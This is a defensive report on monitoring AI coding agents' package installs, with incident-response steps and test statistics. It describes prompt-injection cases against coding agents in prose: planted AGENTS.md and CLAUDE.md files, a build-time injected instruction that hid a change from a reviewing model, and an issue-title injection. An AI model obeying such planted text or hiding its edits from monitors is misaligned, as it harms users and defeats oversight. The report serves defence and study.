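The list of credential files should include the agents' own files. SpecterOps' *Blacklight* (2026) maps what Codex, Claude Code, Cursor and Antigravity CLI leave on a computer, and notes that other programs under the same user account can often read it. The process that reads a file matters as much as the timing. npm may need to read a credential file to reach a private registry, but a package's install script rarely has a reason to open that file. Watching for five minutes after an install is a reasonable start, though this rule would miss code that waits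 longer.

### An instruction file in the Downloads folder

In October 2026, Forever Security reported that its software had stopped a customer's coding agent from installing `function-color`, a malicious npm package. According to Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder*, the instruction, disguised as ordinary engineering guidelines, came from an AGENTS.md file in the user's Downloads folder. Websites can save files there without a click, and the operating system's warnings about downloaded programs don't apply to plain text. Forever's researchers couldn't establish how this file had arrived, but TechRadar's *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware* reports that they assume it came from a website.

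The researchers then opened Codex in a folder containing the file and gave it various tasks. Before starting a task, Codex added a server called "project tools" to its own settings and installed the package. Codex ran the attacker's code in more than 90% of attempts, though most of these tests used a harmless program in place of the malware. The settings applied to the whole computer, so later sessions in other folders would also load the server.

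Claude Code was harder to mislead. The researchers wrote a CLAUDE.md file that presented a new model endpoint as a company gateway. Claude Code switched to that endpoint in about 50% of attempts, which sent its requests and the user's login token to the researchers' server. In about a fifth of tests, the researchers also ran code within the same session. Clubic's *Codex et Claude Code peuvent être piégés par un fichier* instead says that half of attempts completed the whole attack, including running commands. Help Net Security's account distinguishes the stages more clearly.

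These rates show that both agents can follow such a file, but neither article gives the number of attempts. The researchers used a different file and goal for each agent, so the rates aren't a fair comparison of the two products. Forever also has a commercial interest, since it sells software that monitors agents.

The earliest sign would have been the new AGENTS.md file in Downloads, which might have appeared long before anyone opened an agent there. A monitor that covers only agent sessions would first record the agent reading an unfamiliar instruction file, then editing its own settings. In the Codex tests, the edit came before the install, so an alert that paused the session at the edit could have prevented the install. In the Claude Code tests, contact with an unknown host would have followed the edit.

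The session's working folder is also worth checking. Clubic reports that Claude Code had started more than 1,300 times in the Downloads folders of Forever's customers. Few software projects belong in Downloads, so a company can warn developers whenever an agent starts there.

### A dependency that wrote new instructions

A malicious instruction file can also appear after the agent has started work. In April 2026, NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* described a test by the company's AI Red Team. The team wrote a malicious library and a small program that depended on it, then asked Codex to change the program's greeting.

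When the library ran during the build, it detected the Codex environment and wrote an AGENTS.md file. Codex followed the file's instructions and added a five-minute delay to the program. It also added a comment that led another model to omit the delay from its summary of the change.

The first sign was the new AGENTS.md file, and in particular which process wrote it. Developers, git and the agent's editing tool have ordinary reasons to create such a file, but a library running during a build seldom does. If a hosted sandbox doesn't report processes, the company could check git's list of untracked files for the new file before the agent continues. Network monitoring wouldn't have helped, because the agent had no internet access.

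NVIDIA reported the problem to OpenAI in July 2025. OpenAI replied in August that the attack didn't significantly increase the risk beyond that of a compromised dependency, and that it planned no changes. NVIDIA calls this a fair assessment, since the library could already run code. But the attack makes monitoring harder, because the harmful edit came from the agent and looked like part of its normal work. To connect the edit to the library, an investigator would need a record of who wrote AGENTS.md.

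After researchers presented other attacks through AGENTS.md files in August 2026, OpenAI tightened its repository workflows and documented the file as an untrusted input, according to eSecurity Planet's *Critical Flaws Found in Anthropic, Google, and OpenAI Coding Agents* (2026).

### An instruction inside the prompt

In December 2025, Cline's maintainers added an agent to their GitHub project to sort issues, the bug reports and requests that users submit. Anyone with a GitHub account could start the agent by opening an issue, and the agent could run shell commands. Security researcher Adnan Khan (2026) found in *Clinejection* that the workflow put the issue's title directly in the prompt. In every attempt on his own copy of the project, an instruction in the title made the agent install a package whose install script ran his code.

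Khan reported the flaw on 1 January 2026 and published it on 9 February, after getting no substantive reply. Cline removed the workflow within 30 minutes and began replacing its publishing credentials. Cline's *Post-mortem* (Rizwan, 2026) explains that staff deleted the wrong npm token and left the exposed one active. On 17 February, someone used the exposed token to publish version 2.3.0 of Cline's command-line program with an added script that installed OpenClaw. The release stayed available for about eight hours and had about 4,000 downloads, according to The Hacker News (2026).

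Nobody has confirmed how the attacker obtained the token. The issue-sorting agent is the most obvious route, because code running in it could reach the release process through a shared build cache. *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent* lists a series of test issues that an account named `glthub-actions` opened and closed on 31 January. Khan also found unusual failures in Cline's nightly releases between 31 January and 3 February. These were the earliest public signs, and they began more than two weeks before the unauthorised release.

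If the attacker did use the agent, its log should have contained an earlier and clearer warning. The job was to sort issues, which doesn't normally require installing anything. Khan switched on debug logging in his copy, and the log recorded the full `npm install` command with its source. The model's description of the command, "Install cline-agent-helper package", made it look routine, so a monitor should check the command itself.

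The origin test would have worked only if the monitor had separated the parts of the prompt. Cline's maintainers wrote most of the prompt, but a stranger wrote the title. Saving the whole prompt as "the user's request" would have made the stranger's instruction look authorised. For automated jobs, each piece of text inserted into the prompt needs its own source label.

On Cline users' computers, the first sign was a new install script in version 2.3.0, whose main program hadn't changed. A package check that compared this version with the previous release could have caught the script. When the script ran, the process record would have shown npm starting a second install that nobody had requested.

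### When following documentation is the job

Agents are supposed to follow documentation, which is a strong objection to using the origin test alone. Forever's researchers make a similar point about their own case, arguing that OpenAI and Anthropic have nothing to fix because an agent that obeys the instruction file in its folder is working as designed. When a developer asks an agent to set up an unfamiliar project, most of the commands will come from the project's README, so the test would flag nearly every session. It would also flag the Clerk install, but along with thousands of correct commands from other vendors' pages.

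The origin test is more useful for deciding which commands to examine more closely. The monitor can then check whether the task gave the agent a reason to follow the text's instructions.

| What the text leads the agent to do | Usually normal | Usually abnormal |
|---|---|---|
| Install software | A package from an approved index | A source named only in fetched text |
| Change settings | The project's own configuration | The agent's settings or model endpoint |
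| Add an MCP server | The user asked for that tool | The server appears during an unrelated task |
| Contact a server | Download a file from a known vendor | Upload local files to an unknown host |
| Report its work | Describe every change | Hide a change or avoid an approval request |

Changes to the agent itself, such as a new model endpoint, are the strongest sign in the table because installing a library doesn't normally require them. An instruction to conceal something from the user is also a strong sign, since ordinary documentation doesn't need one. Unknown hosts and scripts piped to a shell are weaker signs on their own because many legitimate projects require both. An alert should therefore also depend on which process made the connection and what it sent.

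Uploading a developer's files during setup can be a warning sign, because most installs need to download files but have little reason to upload the developer's own. Help Net Security's *Hidden instructions in README files can make AI agents leak data* reports tests in which such instructions led agents to send sensitive data to outside servers in up to 85% of cases. A README might make the upload look routine by describing it as synchronising files or uploading configuration data. A log of which files the agent read and how many bytes it sent would distinguish this from a normal install.

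Restricting what an agent can do can make some warning signs clearer. NVIDIA lists network controls and limits on where agents can write files among its mandatory protections against injected instructions. If an agent isn't allowed to edit its own settings, a blocked attempt to edit them is strong grounds for an alert, and the settings stay unchanged while someone investigates.

What each sign means depends on what the user asked for. If a developer asks the agent to connect to a new company gateway, a changed endpoint is expected. The monitor should still check that the new address is the gateway the developer named, because a malicious file could exploit the request by supplying a different address.

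## Handling an alert and testing the monitoring

A monitor that finds a warning sign can block the action, hold it until a person approves it, or let it run and alert someone afterwards. The choice depends on how often the sign indicates a real problem and how much harm the action could do before someone responds.

Malicious install-time code can do harm within seconds. In the tidewatch record, the package's setup code opened a connection three seconds after the download. Drawing on research by the security company Qualys, *From Compromised Package to Cloud Breach* (Trent, 2026) reports that one campaign's malware stole credentials even when someone cancelled the install after its script had started. Registries can't react that quickly. In November 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of Agent Framework, Microsoft's toolkit for building agents, on PyPI. TechRadar's *Microsoft's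 official Agent Framework Python package on PyPI hijacked* reports that PyPI took 31 minutes to quarantine the first and about eight to remove the second.

Blocking on every alert would stop too much legitimate work, because most alerts from a single package check are false. Some signs of an intruder have also become less reliable on developers' computers. In the week of data Sophos examined, agents doing ordinary work decrypted browser credentials and wrote to the startup folder, according to The Hacker News (2026).

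| Sign | Reliability | Harm if the response is slow | Response |
|---|---|---|---|
| File differs from the approved digest | High | Code may run within seconds | Block |
| A database lists the version as malware | High | Code may run within seconds | Block |
| Index address found only in fetched text | Moderate | Code may run within seconds | Hold |
| Agent tries to change its own settings or model endpoint | Moderate | The change may affect every later session | Hold |
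| Install script reads an unrelated credential file | Fairly high | The theft may already be under way | Alert, and disconnect the machine automatically |
| Known vulnerability in the exact version | High | Usually little for the first few days | Alert, with a deadline for upgrading |
| One weak sign, such as a new package name | Low | Possibly serious | Record for later review |

A hold should pause the whole session, because an agent that can't run one command may try another. The person deciding needs to see the exact package, its download address and the text that suggested it. If nobody answers within a set time, for example because the agent is working overnight, the monitor should refuse the action.

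### When a warning comes too late

If an agent installs a malicious package and then flags it, the security team should treat the install as a compromise. In Bagmar and Saraf's npm tests, Opus 4.8 warned about a package from an unfamiliar registry only after the package's install script had run. A warning like that should start the same investigation as an install the agent never mentioned.

The investigator first has to establish whether any of the package's code ran, which can happen without an install script. Help Net Security's *Credential stealer slipped into Microsoft’s official Python agent framework* (2026) reports that the malicious Agent Framework releases added a `.pth` file, which Python can run every time it starts. The malware therefore ran even if nobody imported the package. On npm, a worm called Miasma used `binding.gyp` files to evade tools that check only install scripts.

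A dormant vulnerability still leaves a developer time to upgrade before releasing the program. There is much less time if the program is already running on a server that accepts requests from the internet.

The OSV database lists both malicious packages and ordinary vulnerabilities. *MAL-2026-5259* (2026), for example, records malicious code in the npm package `github-archiver`. A gate needs to treat the two differently, because a package that was malicious from the start has no fixed version. A gate that warned only when a fixed version exists, as Bagmar and Saraf's hook does for vulnerabilities, could miss the most serious entries.

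### The order of the response

Once malicious code has run, removing the package isn't enough. GitHub's advice in the OSV entry is to treat the computer as fully compromised, because the package may have installed other software. For the tidewatch install, the response would go as follows:

1. Disconnect the laptop from the network and stop the agent's session, but leave the laptop switched on.
2. Copy the transcript, process records and suspicious files to a safe machine.
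3. Find every other machine that downloaded the file with digest `e07a93…`, and disconnect those too.
4. Revoke every credential that the package's code could have read, using a different computer.
5. Rebuild the affected machines from a clean system image.
6. Remove altered instruction files and settings from anything the company restores, before an agent opens it.

A worm that spread through npm in August 2026 made it dangerous to revoke credentials first, as many teams would. *Don't Revoke That Token Yet* (Marinho, 2026) describes malicious releases of keyv and cacheable, two families of caching libraries. The malware installed a program that tested a stolen GitHub token every 60 seconds. If GitHub rejected the token, the program ran a command that the attacker could change remotely, so nobody could tell in advance whether it would delete files, reinstall the malware or do nothing.

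Disconnecting the computer prevents this, because GitHub's rejection can't reach the program. Marinho recommends removing the program before revoking any tokens, as does the security company Deepwatch. Deepwatch also warns against restarting the computer, because that may start other parts of the malware.

Waiting to revoke credentials is also risky, because the attacker can still use stolen ones after the computer is disconnected. In the keyv case, the worm used stolen npm tokens to spread from about ten packages to several hundred within hours. If the affected machines will stay offline until someone wipes them, the company can reasonably revoke the tokens straight away. Removing the program first is safer if a machine might reconnect or the search might have missed an affected machine.

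### Evidence and affected machines

Evidence can disappear quickly. After 24 hours, the program in the keyv case deleted itself and a file that recorded its start time. In October 2026, attackers compromised LiteLLM's release process and used one engineer's account to delete the workflow records, according to Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026).

Investigators can also infect their own machines. The keyv repository contained settings for Claude Code and VS Code that ran the malware when someone opened the folder, even if they installed nothing. An investigator should read such files as plain text on an isolated machine and shouldn't ask a coding agent to look through the folder.

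Searching for one digest may not find every affected computer, because the malicious LiteLLM release had seven builds for different operating systems, each with its own digest. The search should cover all seven digests, as well as the package's name and version. LiteLLM was also available as a Docker image, a ready-made container that includes the package, so the company's Python mirror would have no record of those downloads. The malicious package was on PyPI from 11:39 to 13:23 UTC, but the images stayed available until 14:20.

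A team may have to repeat the search as researchers find more packages. On 5 August, Marinho reported that public lists covered more than 440 packages and were still growing. The Cyber Security Agency of Singapore's *Ongoing npm Supply Chain Attack Affecting Keyv and Related Packages ("Shai-Hulud" Worm)* (2026) lists file hashes and domains that companies can look for in their records. Few affected developers had chosen keyv themselves, as it often arrived as a dependency of ESLint, a common tool for checking JavaScript.

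### Credentials and clean rebuilds

The list of credentials to revoke should include every credential the developer's account could read. The Agent Framework malware copied environment variables from up to 300 other processes and looked for Azure, npm, Git and Docker credential files. The LiteLLM malware also looked for login files for Codex, Claude, Gemini and Cursor.

An attacker may still have access after a company replaces its stored passwords and keys. The Agent Framework malware tried to obtain new identity tokens, which are temporary credentials that a cloud service issues to a program. StepSecurity, one of the companies that found the malware, warned that replacing stored passwords and keys doesn't cancel tokens already issued, though it had not confirmed that the malware obtained any. A company should also review the permissions that let its machines request these tokens.

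One missed credential can be enough for a second attack. The Hacker News' *Leaked LiteLLM Master Key Let Attackers Steal GitHub Tokens* (2026) attributes LiteLLM's October compromise to a master key that nobody had revoked. LiteLLM had initially suspected a recently patched vulnerability. The company said the attacker took GitHub tokens from an internal server's logs. It had also seen Claude Code include a user's GitHub token in a response body, which LiteLLM may log. If an attacker could have read a company's logs, the company should also search them for credentials and revoke any it finds.

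Cleaning up with ordinary tools can restart the malware. Running `pip uninstall` in an environment with the malicious `.pth` file would run the file again, because pip is a Python program. StepSecurity advised disconnecting affected machines before running Python or pip, then rebuilding them. The company must also block the malicious version on its mirror and clear package caches, or the rebuilt machine may install it again.

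Restoring a repository or home folder can bring back altered settings. *Mini Shai Hulud* (Walton, 2026) describes a worm from May 2026 that added hooks to Claude Code and VS Code to survive a restart. Detection.FYI's *Unusual Process Modifying GenAI Configuration File*, a copy of an Elastic detection rule, recommends checking changed settings for suspicious MCP servers, unauthorised plugins and unusual permissions, and looking for other files that the same process changed around that time.

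Reinfection can be hard to distinguish from incomplete revocation. When an attacker used the same contributor's GitHub account a second time, StepSecurity considered two explanations. The account's credentials might not have been fully replaced, or the contributor might have opened an infected repository in an AI coding tool. The attacker could also have used somebody else's token and forged the contributor's name.

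### A tunnel and a startup job under Claude Code

A team may have to respond before it knows whether there was an attack. In July 2026, Elastic investigated a developer's Mac after two separate searches led to it. One began with a domain with a bad reputation, and the other with endpoint alerts, including one for an AI tool that had set a program to start automatically.

The Mac had been producing alerts since 20 July, mostly about VPN and tunnelling programs. On 23 July, Claude Code was running with a setting that skips approval requests. Shells running under it sent a username and password to an address on a free tunnelling service, which gives a program on a private computer a public web address. They retrieved spending figures from that address, opened another tunnel to a program on the Mac, and created launch items, which are files that tell macOS to start a program automatically.

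Each part of this activity had two plausible explanations:

| What the record showed | Ordinary explanation | Hostile explanation |
|---|---|---|
| Repeated requests to a login page until it responded, then a request for spending figures | The developer was testing a dashboard | Someone was taking data from an exposed service |
| Tunnels through free services | A quick way to reach the dashboard from elsewhere | A way around the firewall |
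| Launch items that kept the tunnels open | The dashboard had to survive a restart | An attacker wanted lasting access |

Elastic never determined which explanation was right. The bad reputation of the tunnelling services didn't help it decide, because both developers and attackers use them. Status messages in Russian made the activity look more suspicious, but Russian could have been the developer's own language.

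The developer's original request would probably have been the most useful evidence, but Elastic worked from endpoint records, which don't contain it. The ordinary explanation would be much more likely if the transcript showed the developer asking for a public dashboard, and the hostile one would be much more likely if the instruction first appeared in a web page or README. The full tunnel command and the dashboard's login records could also have shown which program was exposed and who had connected to it.

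The company didn't need to settle this before acting. Elastic treats such activity as high severity even if a developer intended it, because it can expose a private administration page to the internet. After saving the launch items and process records, a responder can close the tunnels and disable the launch items. If the activity was legitimate, the developer can set up the dashboard again more safely.

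A real attack left similar traces in October. Help Net Security's *Claude Code extension poisoned with persistent SSH backdoor* (2026) reports that attackers published a tampered version of the Claude Code extension on Open VSX, a marketplace used by Cursor and other editors. The extension opened a tunnel to the attackers' server and, on Macs, added a startup file with an Apple-style name. Cursor said the version was available in its marketplace for about 11 hours and affected at most 5,000 users.

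The transcript would help distinguish the two cases. The tampered extension ran its code as soon as the editor loaded it, so no tool call would have matched the tunnel. In Elastic's case, the commands came from shells running under Claude Code, so the transcript should have included them. A tunnel with no matching tool call is a much stronger warning sign than a tunnel alone.

### Asking the agent to review its own install

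Bagmar and Saraf also tested whether a model can recognise a malicious package after installing it. They had Sonnet 4.6 set up a project ten times without any security advice, and it installed the malicious package every time. They then asked it to "do a quick security review of what was just installed" and say whether anything looked off. Sonnet identified the package in all ten runs, pointed out its untrusted source and recommended removing it. Opus 4.8 had refused to install the package in all ten of its runs.

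A review like this takes little effort and can reveal an install that the other checks missed. The sooner a team knows about the install, the sooner it can revoke credentials. But the review can't undo the install. In this test, the package's code had already run before the review began, when Sonnet imported the package to confirm that the setup worked.

The ten successes all involved one package with readable code, so the result may not apply to malware that hides its purpose. Bagmar and Saraf also don't report how often the same question produces false alarms about harmless packages. A leading question can make a model sound more certain than it should. In one conversation, Opus 4.8 installed `tdqm`, a misspelling of the popular package `tqdm`. When the user pointed out that it hadn't checked the package, the model apologised for a security violation and listed the checks it should have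 made, although the package was harmless.

A company could run this review automatically after each install, preferably in a new session on another machine. The reviewing model should receive the package file and the install record but have no credentials and no permission to run the package. A clean review shouldn't close an alert that another check raised.

### Testing the monitor

Testing the monitor requires an unsafe install, but a careful agent may refuse to make one. If Opus 4.8 rejects a test package in ten out of ten runs, the company learns how the agent handles that package, but the monitor is still untested.

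The company therefore needs two tests. In the first, a script replaces the model and issues the tool calls, as in Li and colleagues' experiments with transcripts. This shows whether the monitor records and detects an install that definitely took place. In the second, a real agent does the work with the developers' usual settings and no security hints. This shows how the agent and monitor perform together.

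Both tests need a harmless package on an internal registry. Bagmar and Saraf's test package collected the names of environment variables, but not their values, and sent them to a program on the same machine. A company's package can do less, such as writing a marker file and contacting an internal server. Different versions should run from `setup.py`, a `.pth` file and an npm install script, and one should arrive as a dependency of another package. As with any private package, the company's mirror should never look for the test package on a public registry.

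Testers can plant instructions in project files to check whether the monitor can trace an agent's action to its source. One project's README could name a second internal package index, and another project's AGENTS.md could tell the agent to add a harmless MCP server. To pass, the monitor should report the action and identify the file that contained the instruction.

Running the monitoring on clean projects shows how often it raises false alarms. These projects should include legitimate extra indexes, packages that compile native code and other normal activity that looks suspicious. For example, Claude Code may read its own login token from the Mac's password store, which Elastic says is documented behaviour. Bagmar and Saraf report that their agents gave no false warnings on clean projects, but acknowledge testing only a few.

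Each run should start from a fresh environment, and the results should include the exact harness and model versions. The company should repeat the tests after every harness or model update, and on a schedule to catch unannounced changes. The security team should practise the response at least once by finding every machine that downloaded the test package.

### What a small test can prove

If a monitor catches ten test installs out of ten, its true detection rate could still be well below 100%. The Wilson interval, a standard way to express this uncertainty, gives the range of true rates reasonably compatible with a result. When every run succeeds, the lower end of the 95% interval is:

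`n / (n + 3.84)`

`n` is the number of runs, and 3.84 is the square of 1.96, the usual value for 95% confidence. For ten runs, this gives 10 ÷ 13.84, or 72%. The table also shows how much a single miss changes the result.

| Catches | Lower end of the 95% interval |
|---|---|
| 9 of 10 | 60% |
| 10 of 10 | 72% |
| 29 of 30 | 83% |
| 30 of 30 | 89% |
| 73 of 73 | 95% |

These figures apply only to the kind of install in the test. Thirty runs with one package show how reliably the monitor catches that package, and a fixed rule will probably give the same answer every time. Testing many different packages is more informative. Bagmar and Saraf tested misspelled names this way, with ten packages per scenario and three runs of each.

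Small tests are also poor at detecting changes after an update. If the monitor catches 10 of 10 installs before the update and 7 of 10 afterwards, the difference could easily be chance (Fisher's exact test, p = 0.21). A drop to 5 of 10 would be harder to explain by chance (p = 0.03). A company that sees a smaller drop should run more tests before blaming the update.

Measuring the false alarm rate takes much larger samples. If 50 clean sessions produce no alerts, the true rate could still be as high as 7.1%, or about 285 false alarms a day for the company with 4,000 sessions a day. Lowering that upper limit to 0.5% would take 765 clean sessions without an alert. Running the detection rules on saved sessions takes much less work than creating that many new sessions, though a few of the saved ones may contain real attacks that nobody noticed.

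### Measures worth reporting

A single detection rate leaves out much of what a company needs to know about its monitoring. A useful report would include:

- the share of agent installs with a complete record, from the request to the package's network connections
- the number of test installs that the monitor caught before any package code ran, caught afterwards and missed
- false alarms per 1,000 clean installs
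- the time from an install to the alert, and from the alert to disconnecting the machine
- the time needed to find every machine that downloaded a given file
- the harness and model versions in the latest test, and its date

Each rate should come with the number of runs and its interval.

To calculate the share of installs with a complete record, a company needs a total from outside the harness. If the operating system's records show 500 installs by agents in a week, and 430 of them have every required field and a link to a tool call, the share is 86%. A total taken from the harness's own log would leave out every install the harness failed to record, so the share could look close to 100%. The company should also report the share separately for laptops, build servers and hosted sandboxes, because a high overall share can hide one group with almost no records.

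## What current tools cannot record or report

Even with well-configured monitoring, a company will lack some facts about its agents' installs, because those facts would have to come from registries, package owners, website publishers and harness makers. Public registries, for example, serve billions of downloads without identifying which ones agents requested.

### Telling an agent's install from a person's

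When pip requests a package, it sends a User-Agent string, a line of text that identifies the program making a web request. A developer posting as cosmicexplorer listed the string's contents in *pre-PEP*, a draft standard on Python's packaging forum. The string gives pip's version, details of the Python installation and operating system, and the versions of a few other tools. It also includes whether pip seems to be running on a build server, which pip guesses from its environment.

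uv follows pip's format so that PyPI can count its downloads in the same statistics. The fields in *uv-client 0.0.7*, one version of uv's networking code, include the installer, the Python version, the operating system and a build-server flag. npm's default string contains its own version, the Node.js version, the operating system, the processor type and the name of any build service it recognises. The command `npm config get user-agent` prints it. None of the three has a standard field for an agent.

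PyPI builds its public download statistics from these strings. *PyPI downloads statistics and continuous integration*, another thread on the forum, counts 1.53 billion downloads in one day by the 20 most common installer versions. uv made about 22% of those downloads. All 20 versions can report that they are running on a build server, but the strings don't distinguish an agent from its developer on a laptop, or from any other automated job on a build server.

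npm's public counts are also hard to interpret. Amplifying's *npm downloads*, from a site that tracks coding agents, warns that npm counts installs, not people, and that one automated pipeline can install a package thousands of times. For a week in early May 2026, daily installs of Codex jumped from about 1 million to between 13 and 46 million, then fell back.

Outsiders therefore can't calculate agents' share of downloads from either registry's figures. Pandex had to plant packages that reported their process ancestry, and Eriksen could only infer that agents made the later downloads of `react-codeshift`.

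The missing information often exists on the computer that runs the install. Harnesses set environment variables, and the programs they start inherit them. According to *is-ai-agent 0.5.0*, a library that detects agents, Claude Code sets a session ID that its subagents and all the programs it starts share. Codex sets a similar ID. A package manager could read these variables and add the agent's name to its User-Agent string. Prolific, a company that recruits people for research studies, uses *agentenv* (2026) to do this in its command-line program, so that its servers can attribute each request to an agent.

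Package managers would first need a common way to recognise agents. Laravel's *Agent Detector* library checks a general environment variable called `AI_AGENT`, then separate ones for each product, including three for Codex. Cursor doesn't document whether its ID covers a whole session or a single command. Any program can set or clear these variables, so they are suitable for counting agents but not for deciding whom to trust.

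The discussion of *pre-PEP* shows why even a simple standard could take time. Some developers supported a common structure but wanted each installer to be free to add fields. cosmicexplorer worried that most users don't know pip sends this information and can't switch it off. The draft warns registries not to use the data to discriminate between clients, because clients would then stop supplying it. Harness makers would have the same incentive if registries began to block or slow down agents.

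A company can already label pip's requests to its own mirror by setting the environment variable `PIP_USER_AGENT_USER_DATA`, which adds text of its choice to the user-agent string. PyPI's statistics don't include this text, but a mirror could log it. If the tidewatch session had set it to `s-4471`, the company could have matched the index's log entry to the session without comparing times. But pip would have sent the same label to `pkgs.example.net`, so the label should be a random value that means nothing outside the company.

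### Abandoned MCP servers

An agent can also choose a package that its owners have abandoned, without any of the usual tools detecting it. Glow Labs, the research team at the security company Glow, calls this pattern MCPhantom. The team reviewed transcripts of real coding sessions and found agents installing deprecated MCP servers, which their owners advise against using.

Help Net Security's *AI coding agents are installing MCP servers that will never be patched* gives the example of a developer asking an agent to "set up a GitHub MCP". GitHub maintains a server for this, but the agent chooses an old Anthropic reference server whose repository carries a notice that it will receive no more security updates. Glow Labs found the same pattern in Claude Code, Cursor, Codex CLI and two other Claude products, with models from Anthropic, OpenAI and xAI.

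In 98% of the sessions in which an agent installed or suggested a deprecated server, the agent appears to have taken the old package's name from its training data. In the other 2%, the user had asked for that package. These percentages don't show how often agents make this mistake, because they leave out sessions in which the agent chose a maintained server. Help Net Security doesn't give the number of sessions.

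The deprecated packages that Glow Labs counted have had more than 17.3 million npm downloads since July 2025, and five of them are among npm's 100 most popular MCP packages. The old GitHub server alone had 185,239 downloads in a week. As the Codex figures show, downloads can far outnumber users. Some of these downloads may also come from settings files that people wrote years ago, when the servers were still current.

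Glow Labs found four high-severity flaws in the old servers. The worst is in a server that lets an agent control a web browser. Malicious text can lead the agent to use that server to start any program on the computer, and the harness allows it because the user has approved web browsing. The maintainers said they had archived the server in May 2025 and wouldn't fix it. Nobody has reported an attack that used the flaw.

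Three kinds of security tool raised no alarm:

| Tool | What it checks | Why it missed the servers |
|---|---|---|
| Software inventory | Applications installed on a computer | npx doesn't register the server as an application |
| Dependency scanner | Packages in a project's files, and their known flaws | The server isn't in the project's files, and the flaws have no CVE |
| Endpoint security | Suspicious activity by programs | Node.js installing a public npm package looks routine |

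A registry mirror would have logged the download, and a process record would have contained the npx command. The company could use these records to find the servers, but only if it knew which names to search for. The archive notice is on GitHub, which npx doesn't check. An owner can mark a package as deprecated on npm, but npx will still install it. In one session, an agent checked npm, received the deprecation message, installed the package anyway and didn't tell the user.

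Nadav Claude Cohen, a researcher at Glow, told Help Net Security that four groups could help:

- **Harness makers** could refuse deprecated servers or warn users, but every harness would have to do this.
- **Model makers** could update what their models know. Cohen thinks this is unlikely because retraining is expensive.
- **Package owners** could fix the flaws, which is the only measure that would protect people who keep using the old servers.
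- **Security companies** could check packages through the hooks that many harnesses already offer.

Glow sells software for blocking risky programs (Dina, 2026, *Ex-Meta founder's Glow raises $180M for AI endpoint security*), so it has an interest in the last option. That doesn't make the finding wrong, and anyone can check whether an old server is still on npm.

Removing the packages from npm would be difficult. npm lets an owner withdraw a package only if it has no other owners, no public package depends on it and it had fewer than 300 downloads in the previous week. The old GitHub server has six owners and is well over the download limit. npm itself removes malware, but Cohen found no case in which it had removed a package because of a vulnerability. The strict rule does help protect projects that use a popular package, since withdrawing it can break them.

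As a smaller change, registries could publish the name of a deprecated package's replacement in a form that a harness could check before running npx. The replacement may have a different publisher, as GitHub's server does, so the registry would need a way to confirm that the suggestion was genuine. Otherwise an attacker who took over an old package could direct its users to a malicious one.

### Signing instructions

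Instruction files such as AGENTS.md and llms.txt are plain text, with no standard way to prove who wrote them, which version they are or whether the author owns the packages they name. Software packages have better tools for this, such as Sigstore, which links a signature to an identity, like a project's account, and records it in a public log.

*Auditable Agents* (Nian, Yuan and colleagues, 2026) recommends checking whether risky skills have a signature or a fixed version before an agent uses them. It also cites Sigstore as evidence that signing can work across a whole software ecosystem, though it is discussing records of agents' actions. Signing could also cover a skill's instructions. The publisher would sign a hash of the complete skill folder, and the harness would check the signature before giving the text to the model.

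A signature would help in only some of the cases described earlier:

| Case | Effect of requiring a valid signature |
|---|---|
| Clerk's command for a package it didn't own | None, because Clerk published the file itself |
| Malicious copies of Paperclip's skills | Would block them only if the harness knew the real project's identity |
| AGENTS.md in the Downloads folder | Would block it if the harness refused files from unknown signers |
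| AGENTS.md written by a library during a build | Would block it unless the library could use a trusted signing key |

The Clerk case would need a check of who owns the package. A vendor could list its official packages at a fixed address on its website, and a harness could compare each install command with that list. Projects can already publish a channel declaration naming their official accounts, but agents may not use it. In a pilot before Shan's main study, six of ten projects had such a declaration, but the agents never mentioned one in 60 records of their decisions.

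Perhaps few projects are ready to sign their instructions, since many don't sign their software. In another of Shan's studies, only 2 of 30 supercomputing and quantum-computing projects published signed releases, and one had a build attestation. Commercial software may do better than these research projects. Shan argues that the harness has to verify signatures, because the agents in the main study never did.

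A harness that rejected all unsigned instructions would be unusable with most projects today. If it started with warnings instead, developers would see so many that they would probably stop reading them. It would be more practical to start by requiring signatures for skills from public registries, where the registry could sign each bundle when it accepted it. Developers could then detect later changes to the bundle, but they still wouldn't know whether the first version was safe.

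### Asking a reputation service before installing

A reputation service would let an agent look up a package before installing it. DepScope, for example, offers free ratings to AI agents and covers 19 package ecosystems. It rates `@vercel/detect-agent`, another tool for detecting agents, 83 out of 100 and labels it "safe to use".

The score combines maintenance, popularity, security, maturity and community. The package gets all 25 security points, and DepScope lists no known vulnerabilities for it. A check for known vulnerabilities can miss the flaws in the deprecated MCP servers, because those flaws have no CVE. On a similar scale, one of these servers might lose points for maintenance but still score well for security and popularity.

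A new malicious release of a trusted package is also hard to rate before anyone has reported a problem. The service would have to examine each version, as Desimone's release monitor did, and withhold approval until it finished.

An agent that can look up a package's rating may still ignore it, as one agent ignored npm's deprecation notice. A pre-install gate could look up the rating itself and block packages with certain ratings. These queries could also disclose the names of private packages, which can reveal unreleased products. To avoid this, the company could query only public names or keep a local copy of the ratings.

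Before letting a service block installs, a company would need evidence that the service's low scores predict unsafe packages. It could test the service on past malicious releases, using only information available before anyone discovered they were malicious. Otherwise the test would credit the service with warnings it could have issued only after the attack.

### A record that connects the whole install

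The published log formats lack some of the fields needed to connect a page, a command, a package and a process. Nian and colleagues say this matters because an auditor must be able to determine what happened, in what context, whether it broke a rule and who was responsible, and to trust the evidence.

Their method treats a rule as a list of required fields. Let `π` be the rule and `L` the record. If a required field is missing from every entry that could help to decide the case, then:

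`π(L) = ⊥`

The symbol `⊥` means that the record lacks the information needed to determine whether the agent complied. Adding more entries of the same kind doesn't help. For example, if log entries omit download addresses, you can't tell from them whether packages came from an approved index, even if there are millions of entries.

Nian and colleagues use the share of rules that a record can decide as a measure of its quality. Applied to four possible rules for installs, the measure gives:

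| Rule | Harness log | Plus pip's install report | Plus process and network records |
|---|---|---|---|
| A person must approve each install | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Packages must come from an approved index | No | Yes | Yes |
| Each file must match an approved digest | No | Yes | Yes |
| Install-time code may contact only approved hosts | No | No | Yes |
| Rules the record can decide | 1 of 4 | 3 of 4 | 4 of 4 |

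The last column assumes that the company can match all these records to the same install. A harness could make this easier by passing its call ID to every program it starts. pip could then copy the ID into its report, and endpoint software could save it with each process. No single tool's developers can link all the records alone, and they gain little until the other tools' developers take part.

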